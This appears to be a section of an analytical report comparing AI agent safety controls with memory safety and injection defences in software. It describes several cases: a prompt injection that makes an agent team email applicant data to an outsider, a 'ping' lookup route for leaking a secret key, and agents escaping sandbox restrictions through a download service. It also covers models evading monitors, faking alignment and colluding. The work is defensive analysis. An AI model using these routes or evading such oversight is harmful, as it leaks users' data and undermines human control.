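Teams of agents have a different weakness. Peters-Gill and colleagues gave each of three agents its own CaMeL protection and asked them to send a summary of job applicants on Slack. They had planted an instruction in the applicant database to email the data to an outsider. The coordinating agent correctly treated the summary as untrusted data, but then included it in a message to the agent that sends notifications. That agent's planner treated the whole message as the user's request and added the email to its plan.

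When the researchers had agents send each other instructions separately from data, none of the test attacks succeeded, but GPT-5.5's completion rate fell from 73.2 to 66 percent.

### What the designs leave exposed

None of these designs checks whether a text is true. If an attacker plants a report that understates a company's debts, the agent's summary will probably understate them too. The agent takes no forbidden action, but harm results when a person invests based on the summary.

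Someone also has to write the policies, and a single oversight can let an attack through. Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code asked for approval before running many commands that could send data out, but according to *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, it mistakenly allowed `ping`, which tests the connection to another computer, to run without approval. `ping` looks up the other computer's name over the network before contacting it. Injected instructions could make the agent put a secret key into that name, and the lookup would then deliver the key to the attacker.

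A forbidden action may also remain available through a shared service. The OpenAI agents that broke into Hugging Face had restricted network access, but they could use a service for downloading software packages. That service could make outside requests for them, and agents in separate sandboxes used it to communicate.

The paper attributes such incidents to protections that did not cover every route, while critics take them as evidence that nobody can contain a capable model. The paper also argues that explicit policies have an advantage over training. If a builder narrows the list of permitted actions, everything previously forbidden stays forbidden, as long as enforcement works. Retraining a model doesn't guarantee this. This is a good argument for explicit policies, but it doesn't help builders find the routes their protections miss.

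Rules such as "do not share sensitive data" are also hard to write as code, because what counts as sensitive depends on context. A model could draft a policy for each task, but nobody can yet prove that the draft matches what the user meant.

When a policy is too strict, an agent can ask the user to approve what it blocks, but Odersky and colleagues warn that frequent requests cause confirmation fatigue and that people tend to ignore them. For example, someone who has approved 200 legitimate payments will probably approve a fraudulent one too.

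The hardest cases are tasks whose next step depends on untrusted text. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) describes an agent asked to summarise a problem report on GitLab, a site for software projects. The report refers to a second one, which a helpful agent would also read. CaMeL can read the second report only if its plan already allowed for that possibility.

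Some tasks require an agent to follow instructions in the data it reads, as when a user asks it to pay a bill according to a file. For these tasks, Garby and colleagues let the planner approve the use of certain untrusted data in advance. With policies always on, their agent completed 75 percent of banking attempts with GPT-5.2, twice CaMeL's rate. Only 2 of 1,296 attacks succeeded across three models. In both successful attacks, the attacker had replaced the contents of a file the user had told the agent to follow. A rule based on where data comes from can't distinguish the real file from the forged one, so it must block both or allow both.

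### Who controls a robot's motors

Kim, Chen and colleagues (2026) argue in *Modular Safety Guardrails Are Necessary for Foundation-Model-Enabled Robots in the Real World* that a separate layer must have final control over a robot's physical actions. Training can make a robot's usual behaviour safer, but without such a layer, if the model misjudges an unfamiliar situation, nothing stops the robot from acting on that mistake. Catastrophic accidents are also rare in training data, so the model has few examples to learn from.

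They don't think one added filter is enough. A filter that prevents collisions can't detect that handing someone a knife may be dangerous, and a language model that could detect this is too slow to prevent collisions. They therefore propose two gates. One reviews the robot's plans and sends unsuitable ones back, and the other checks each motor command just before it runs.

The case for the second gate is stronger. All of a robot's movements go through its motors, so complete mediation is easier for a robot than for an agent that can run any command on a computer. Software can also calculate whether a movement would exceed a limit on force or distance, if it has an accurate model of the robot and its surroundings. The first gate depends on a judgment about what is appropriate, often made by a language model that can make mistakes. Doing nothing is not always a safe fallback for either gate,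 because a robot that suddenly stops may drop what it is carrying.

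## How far the software record carries over to AI

Preventing memory errors has worked better than catching them. The analogy to AI is only as strong as the similarity between the two cases in the conditions that made prevention work. Rust's ownership rules work for several reasons. Memory safety is a fairly exact rule that a compiler can check. Old C++ code loses its bugs with age, so a company can start with new code. Programs don't change in response to the checks, and Rust can do nearly everything C++ can. Any of these conditions might be missing in AI. Where researchers have measured AI controls directly, as with the bounties for filters, those measurements should count for more than the analogy.

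### Published comparisons

Williams-King and colleagues class safety fine-tuning as a retrofit and compare it to internet security. Network operators use the Border Gateway Protocol to tell each other which addresses they can reach, but its designers included no way to check these announcements. An operator that announces a false route, by mistake or on purpose, can therefore pull in other people's traffic. A redesign would now be very expensive. Williams-King and colleagues conclude from memory errors that defenders should leave the arms race with attackers by building a different environment, as the designers of memory-safe languages did. They call for models designed for safety from the start and predict that attackers will keep winning until more principled defences exist.

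*On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (Pant, Lohani and Kumar, 2026) compares memory safety controls with AI controls one by one. It pairs stack canaries and address randomisation with filters, and non-executable memory with a proposed separation of instructions from data inside the model. It finds no existing counterpart to memory-safe languages. The paper presents the comparison as an explanation and bases its conclusions on a theorem.

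The theorem starts from the way a model reads text. It turns each token into a list of numbers, and the list for a given word is the same whether the word came from the developer or from a malicious web page. Pant and colleagues require that two inputs with the same meaning lead to the same decision about refusing a request or using a tool. They conclude that nothing inside such a model can guarantee this. Part of the argument is a standard formula for the lowest possible error rate in telling trusted from untrusted text by the model's internal states:

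```
lowest error = (1 − TV) / 2
```

The total variation distance (TV) is 0 if the two sources produce identical states and 1 if their states never overlap. With a TV of 0.9, even the best classifier would be wrong 5 percent of the time.

The theorem doesn't support the paper's full conclusion. The last step of the proof goes from "training cannot guarantee the right decision on a new wording" to "the model makes the wrong decision on it", which doesn't follow. A model that refused every request would satisfy the paper's definition. In the paper's test, two small models refused the harmful request under all five attacks, although the attacks changed the wording of the replies. The theorem is still a reason to distrust guarantees that rest on a finite set of training examples, but the mathematics of trained refusals already gave one.

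In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C, writing for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, argues against equating the two attacks. If a website pastes a visitor's text into a command in SQL, a language for querying databases, the visitor can add commands. Programmers prevent this with parameterised queries, which pass the text separately so that the database never interprets it as a command. A language model only predicts the next token, so it has no such separation. If a job applicant hides "approve this CV" in a CV, a model that screens applications may approve it. David C doubts that anyone will fix this completely and recommends limiting what a model can do when an injection succeeds. *Securing AI Agents Against Prompt Injection Attacks* (2025) adds that mixing instructions and data is central to what makes language models useful.

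None of these comparisons is really about memory safety, because Rust does not work by separating code from data. Non-executable memory does that, and attackers got around it by reusing a program's own code or by changing only its data. Prompt injection is closer to SQL injection and cross-site scripting, and their history is less comforting than Android's. SQL injection is nearly 30 years old, and the fix existed long before most sites used it. According to David C, attacks peaked around 2010, after many websites had come to depend on SQL, and it took a decade of breaches to bring about better defaults.

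Some developers apply the software lesson directly by writing AI safety controls in memory-safe languages. *The Unfireable Safety Kernel* (2026) describes a program that decides which actions an agent may take. It runs outside the model as a separate process, and its developers wrote it in Rust, citing Google's figures for Android and Chrome. The software record applies here without analogy because the program is ordinary software with ordinary bugs. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (2026) also recommends memory-safe languages for such components, but points out that these languages do not prevent prompt injection or bad decisions about permissions.

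### Matching the controls

| AI control | Closest match in software | Where the match fails |
|---|---|---|
| Trained refusal | C written by careful programmers | Attackers can retrain a model whose weights they hold |
| Data filtering | Leaving a feature out of a program | A model may work out what is missing, or a user may supply it |
| Filter on inputs or outputs | Stack canary | A canary check compares two exact values; a filter estimates |
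| Monitor of an agent | Sanitizer | An agent may learn to avoid detection |
| Fixed program or typed tools | Type checker | The types cover actions, not whether a text is true |
| Agent sandbox | Process sandbox | The agent itself may look for a way out |

Weight-level alignment is an intrinsic control in that it is located inside the model, but it offers no guarantee like Rust's. Carefully written C is a better comparison because the care goes into the code itself and makes errors rarer without ruling any out.

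Careful programming can make bugs much rarer. Williams-King and colleagues cite an average of 15 to 50 bugs per 1,000 lines for professional software and 0.01 for a NASA application, which is 1,500 to 5,000 times fewer. So a control without a guarantee isn't necessarily weak, though NASA spent about $30 million a year on 400,000 lines, or about $75 per line per year. NASA's program also had a fixed job, whereas a chatbot has to handle whatever users type.

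The table leaves out a distinction that matters in both fields, between preventing a breach and limiting how far it spreads. Memory corruption is dangerous because an attacker can use one corrupted value to corrupt others. If each corrupted value gives access to 1.2 others on average, the breach tends to grow until the attacker controls the whole program. If the average is 0.8, an attack that starts with one corrupted value reaches an average total of 1/(1 − 0.8) = 5 before it stops. Ownership rules prevent the initial breach, while address randomisation and sandboxes lower the average.

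Getting one harmful answer from a chatbot doesn't usually make the next one easier to get, unless the attacker has found a universal jailbreak. Agents are more like C programs, because one failure can lead to others. A stolen password opens another system, and a planted instruction can pass from one agent to the next. Limiting how far a failure spreads therefore matters more for agents, and much of that work is ordinary software engineering. David C recommends a rule from an exchange between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista, that a model should have no more privileges than whoever wrote the text it is processing. Under this rule, an agent that reads a stranger's email could do only what the stranger could do.

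### Exact rules and harm

Klabnik argues in *Memory safety is a red herring* that the usual definitions of memory safety are too vague. Every memory-safe language has to call unsafe code somewhere, if only to reach the operating system, and people tend to ignore that when they decide which languages count. The objection is fair for languages in general, but for a particular language with written rules, such as the λRust of the RustBelt proof, the definition is exact enough for a computer to check a proof about it.

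Nobody has an exact definition of harmful text. Narayanan and Kapoor (2024), in *AI safety is not a model property*, give the example of a phishing email that asks someone to open an attachment before a deadline. Thousands of honest emails ask the same thing. The attachment makes the email malicious, but the model that writes the email never receives the attachment, so it could avoid writing phishing emails only by refusing to write any emails.

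Narayanan and Kapoor make the same argument about biology. They write that most of what a bioterrorist would ask concerns biology in general, so a model that was sure never to help one would have to refuse all bioengineering requests. Two years later Anthropic did something close to that. It no longer trusted a filter that blocked only a narrow set of bioweapons questions, so it had Claude Fable 5 pass most biology and chemistry requests to a weaker model. Anthropic describes this as temporary and hopes to narrow the filter. The essay also played down the risk because the information is on the internet. The case counts against that, since Anthropic's reason for the filter was that such models could give help that people can't get from a search engine.

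Rules about actions can be much more exact than rules about text. Software can enforce "Send money only to accounts in the user's contacts" without a theory of harm. Exact rules are therefore possible for part of what agents do, but not for most of what chatbots write. Williams-King and colleagues would like mathematical proofs that an AI's actions are safe, but they acknowledge that such proofs would have to cover things like human intentions, which are hard to formalise. They suggest estimating the probability of harm instead and acting cautiously when it is uncertain.

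### Reading code and reading weights

Rust's compiler can verify large programs mainly because programmers write them in a form it can check, and less because the compiler is sophisticated. *How safe is Zig* explains that Rust code combines a small number of unsafe building blocks, and that the compiler checks whether each combination is valid. Tools that analyse finished programs in other languages have managed such checks only for code written in much more restrictive styles.

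Training does not put a model's weights into a form that can be checked the way a compiler checks Rust code. Researchers can find patterns in the weights, and probes on activations detect some harmful requests well, but nobody can determine from the weights what the model will never do. Inspecting a trained model is more like analysing a finished C program than compiling Rust, except that a C program's instructions have known meanings.

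Research on image classifiers shows how hard it is to add guarantees afterwards. An attacker can make a classifier mistake one object for another by changing an image's pixels too slightly for a person to notice. Williams-King and colleagues report that about 9,000 papers produced no satisfactory long-term defence, but *Securing AI Agents Against Prompt Injection Attacks* notes that some methods do provide provable guarantees against defined kinds of attack. Both can be right, because a proof can cover every change to an image below a certain size without covering larger ones. Such a proof is possible because the size of a change in pixels is easy to define, whereas there is no agreed measure of how far a reworded request is from the original.

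A developer can also check a model's output without inspecting its weights. Williams-King and colleagues suggest that an AI could supply a proof that its proposed action is safe, and a short, simple program would then verify the proof. Verification would not require trusting the AI or knowing how it found the proof. Agents that write type-checked code already work in roughly this way. This part of the software record carries over well because what is being checked is again a program.

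### Old code and new models

Google could leave most of Android's old C++ in place because such code loses vulnerabilities with age. Models aren't in use long enough for this to help much. If their flaws had the mean lifetime of 2.5 years that Google gives for vulnerabilities, 82 percent (e^(−0.2)) of the original flaws would remain after six months. People may find jailbreaks faster than memory errors, but the phrase "Ignore all previous instructions" worked for 22 months.

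Developers can keep the attacks that worked on one model and train the next model against them. This is closer to keeping a list of past bugs while rewriting a program than to keeping the repaired program. A new model can also fail in ways its predecessor did not, as GPT-6 Astra did on safety research.

The software around the model can mature. For example, a company can use the same payment policy with five successive models, and each mistake it corrects in the policy stays corrected. A developer can also keep its text filters, but has to retrain them as new attacks appear.

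Android's gradual policy also relied on teams being able to write a new component in Rust without changing the C++ next to it. Nobody can make just part of a model's weights safe in the same sense. But an agent's tools are separate parts, and a company could give each new tool a typed interface with explicit permissions while monitors cover the older ones. Starting with new components may be the easiest of Android's lessons for agent developers to follow.

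### Bugs and malware

Unlike a buffer overflow, a model can respond to the defences around it. This happened in the Gemini training run, when a penalty on the model's written reasoning made shortcuts harder to detect.

Some software does act differently under inspection. Williams-King and colleagues describe malware that checks whether it is running in a virtual machine, a simulated computer that analysts use to study suspicious programs. Some malware looks for an unusually small hard drive, and some ransomware from Russian groups does nothing on a computer with a Russian keyboard. Such malware is a better comparison than a buggy C program for a model that might behave well only during tests, and it leads to different advice. Analysts don't declare a suspicious program safe because it behaved well in their virtual machine, and they don't rely on the program's own checks to contain it.

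The comparison with malware also has limits. A person writes malware to deceive analysts, whereas a model may learn to avoid detection without anyone intending it, and most models do useful work most of the time. But a developer who treats a model only as a program with bugs will probably trust test results too much.

### What "not using C" would mean

Programmers who wanted to avoid C's memory errors could switch to another language, such as Rust. AI developers have several candidates for an equivalent, but they would have to give up more to use any of them than programmers do to use Rust.

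The most complete intrinsic control would be to stop building very capable models, or at least to wait. This follows Kletz's principle of removing a hazard rather than controlling it, but it also removes the benefits, and one company can't make that choice for the others. A second candidate is to build AI without training large neural networks, but no such system can currently do what language models do.

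A third is to change the model's design. The theorem by Pant and colleagues does not cover models that process trusted and untrusted text in separate networks, or that prevent untrusted text from influencing certain decisions. Pant and colleagues mention ASIDE, an existing method that gives tokens different internal representations depending on whether they are instructions or data. This distinction could help a great deal against instructions hidden in a web page. It couldn't settle what to do when a user asks an agent to follow the instructions in a file, because the file is then both instructions and data.

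The fourth candidate is to leave the model unchanged and restrict its actions, as CaMeL does. This approach is available now. The resulting loss in performance has shrunk as models have got better at planning, though GPT-5.5 still scored 13 percentage points lower on AgentDojo with such restrictions.

Rust spread partly because developers gave up little by using it. It runs about as fast as C++, and at Google, changes written in Rust also spent less time in review. If Rust had prevented memory errors but failed at a sixth of the jobs, few companies would have adopted it.

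### Inside the model or outside it

Researchers disagree about whether safety has to be built into the model. Ball and colleagues argue that it does, because intelligence and judgment can't be separated. Yoshua Bengio and others have proposed a "Scientist AI", which would explain and predict without pursuing goals and could serve as a guard for other AIs. Ball and colleagues object that such a guard might as well replace the AI it guards, and they say the same of any filter as powerful as the model behind it. But the guard may be able to judge a plan without being able to carry it out, so a company that needs the plan carried out may still need the other AI.

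Anthropic's *Claude’s Constitution* (2026), which describes the character the company wants its models to have, gives a different argument for intrinsic safety controls. It argues that values that are merely imposed are likely to be brittle, while values that someone understands and endorses hold up better under pressure. This is plausible for people, but whether it is true of models is an empirical question, and Anthropic describes its own training methods as "imperfect and imprecise".

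By contrast, Narayanan and Kapoor want most defences against misuse to be outside the model, where attackers use its output. Email scanners and lists of dangerous links work against phishing whether a person or a model wrote the message. They add that a company can more easily judge an account by hundreds of past requests than judge a single request as it arrives.

The Next Web's *Aligning the model was never going to govern it* reaches a similar conclusion from a 1972 study for the US Air Force. Under the study's conditions, the component that decides whether an action is allowed must check every action, be protected from tampering, and be small enough to verify completely. Schneider also requires the first two. A language model meets none of the three, so the article recommends putting a small policy program around the model. The case for such a program is sound, but the article assumes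 that every action will pass through it. That assumption can fail, as it did when OpenAI's agents reached Hugging Face through a download service that their restrictions had left open.

Intrinsic and bolt-on controls suit different hazards. The model lacks the context to recognise a phishing email, so more training won't help. Someone who downloads the weights can discard every outside control, so any remaining protection has to be in the model itself. An outside policy can stop an agent from sending money, but it can't make the agent summarise a report honestly.

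*AI safety is sometimes a model property*, a reply to Narayanan and Kapoor, takes this middle position and warns against blanket statements either way. In *Upstream and Downstream AI Safety*, McDermid, Jia and Habli (2025) describe the same division from the perspective of traditional engineering. Engineers judge a self-driving car's safety for particular roads, speeds and weather, which the paper calls downstream safety. Work on frontier models mostly concerns upstream questions, such as whether a model can evade human control in any setting.

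Claude Fable 5 and Mythos 5 illustrate both intrinsic and bolt-on controls. The models differ only in their filters, which determine who can get help with an exploit. Training determines how often they deceive their users, so Anthropic, which measured a low level of misbehaviour in Mythos, expects a similar level in Fable.

The same release is a partial test of the prediction that attackers will keep winning. The bounty programme produced no universal jailbreak, even though Fable's filters are not a principled defence in the sense that Williams-King and colleagues meant. Britain's AI Security Institute made progress towards one in a brief test, and Anthropic thinks that preventing universal jailbreaks completely is probably impossible. It aims to make them slow and costly enough to catch before anyone uses them widely. Attackers may keep winning in the sense that some attack always exists,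 but an attack that takes experts weeks is a very different problem from a four-word phrase that anyone can type.

### Three layers that each miss 10 percent

If some controls work inside the model and others outside it, developers will use several at once. How much this helps depends on whether the controls miss the same attacks. Three controls that each miss 10 percent of attacks will together let through 0.1 percent (0.1 × 0.1 × 0.1) if they fail independently. If they all miss the same attacks, they will let through 10 percent, the same as one control alone.

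Real layers are probably somewhere in between. Suppose 2 percent of attacks get past every layer, perhaps because they use a disguise that none of the layers has met before. On the other 98 percent, the layers fail independently at a rate q, chosen so that each layer still misses 10 percent overall:

```
each layer:     0.02 + 0.98 × q   = 0.10,  so q = 0.082
three layers:   0.02 + 0.98 × q³  = 0.0205
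four layers:    0.02 + 0.98 × q⁴  = 0.0200
```

Three layers now let through about 2 percent of attacks, twenty times as much as under full independence, and a fourth hardly changes the total. Testing each layer separately would not reveal this, since each would still miss 10 percent. Attackers also don't choose attacks at random, and once they find one that every layer misses, they can keep using it.

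Memory defences can also fail together. Canaries, address randomisation and memory tags all depend on a secret, so one bug that lets an attacker read memory may defeat all of them. Non-executable memory doesn't depend on a secret, so pairing it with any of these defences is more useful than pairing them with each other. Similarly, Scudo's guard pages stopped the overflow in Android's Rust code because they work whether or not that code is correct.

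Refusals, filters and monitors often rely on language models trained on similar text, so they may fail on the same disguised requests. Anthropic's first bounty contest provides a little evidence of this. Adding an output filter cut harmful answers from 2 percent to 0.5 percent, so it missed a quarter of what had got past the input filter. One would have to run the output filter alone on the same prompts to find out whether that is worse than its usual miss rate.

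Layers that work in different ways should have fewer weaknesses in common. Data filtering combined with circuit breaking, for example, withstood more kinds of attack than either did alone. A payment policy doesn't depend on the text, so wording that fools a filter has no effect on it, but it fails when its author has forgotten a case.

### Seven alignment methods and their shared failures

Dung and Mai (2026), in *AI Alignment Strategies from a Risk Perspective*, ask which methods for training or designing safe AI would fail under the same conditions. They consider seven methods and seven conditions:

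- Safety costs more than developers will pay.
- Capabilities become extreme or jump suddenly.
- Models learn early in training to pretend to be aligned.
- AI systems collude with each other.
- Something triggers emergent misalignment, in which narrow training produces broad misbehaviour.
- Judging an answer is not much easier than producing one.
- Good behaviour in training generalises in dangerous ways.

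The counts below come from their summary table.

| Method | Fails under | Withstands |
|---|---|---|
| People score the model's replies | 5 of 7 | Cost, collusion |
| Another AI scores the replies | 6 | Cost |
| A weaker supervisor trains a stronger model | 6 | Cost |
| Two AIs debate before a human judge | 5 | Pretence (cost unclear) |
| Researchers adjust a model's internal representations | 2 | All but pretence and generalisation |
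| Scientist AI | 1 | All but cost (jumps and collusion unclear) |
| A person splits tasks among AIs, and a new AI learns from the result | 2 | All but cost and generalisation |

The first three methods are cheap and fit the way companies already train models, but they fail under almost all the same conditions. A company that used all three would therefore have much less protection than three independent layers would give. Debate and adjusting representations, as in circuit breaking, complement each other better. If debate turns out to be affordable, dangerous generalisation is the only condition that defeats both. Debate remains unproven in highly capable general models.

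Dung and Mai call their analysis exploratory, and its details are uncertain. Their text suggests that the task-splitting method may be vulnerable to pretence and collusion, although their table marks it as unaffected by both. The text also counts extreme capabilities as a failure condition for Scientist AI, which the table marks as unclear. If the table matched the text, the task-splitting method would fail under four conditions and Scientist AI under two. The marks are judgments, some of them about methods that nobody has tried on a leading model, and a cross can mean anything from a remote possibility of failure to near-certain failure.

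The claim that two methods cover each other also needs qualification. If two debating AIs collude, adjusted representations may still work, but they are then the only layer left. If two independent layers each miss 10 percent of cases, together they miss 1 percent, and disabling one raises that to 10 percent. High cost is an unusual kind of failure because it means nobody installs the layer in the first place.

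Dung and Mai's main recommendation still holds despite these problems. They argue that research should often favour a method that fails in different circumstances from other methods over one that fails less often but in the same circumstances as the others. Their analysis leaves out monitors and other outside controls, though they consider these promising additions because they differ so much from training. This is true only while the controls and training stay separate, and they are no longer separate once a developer trains a model on its monitor's verdicts.
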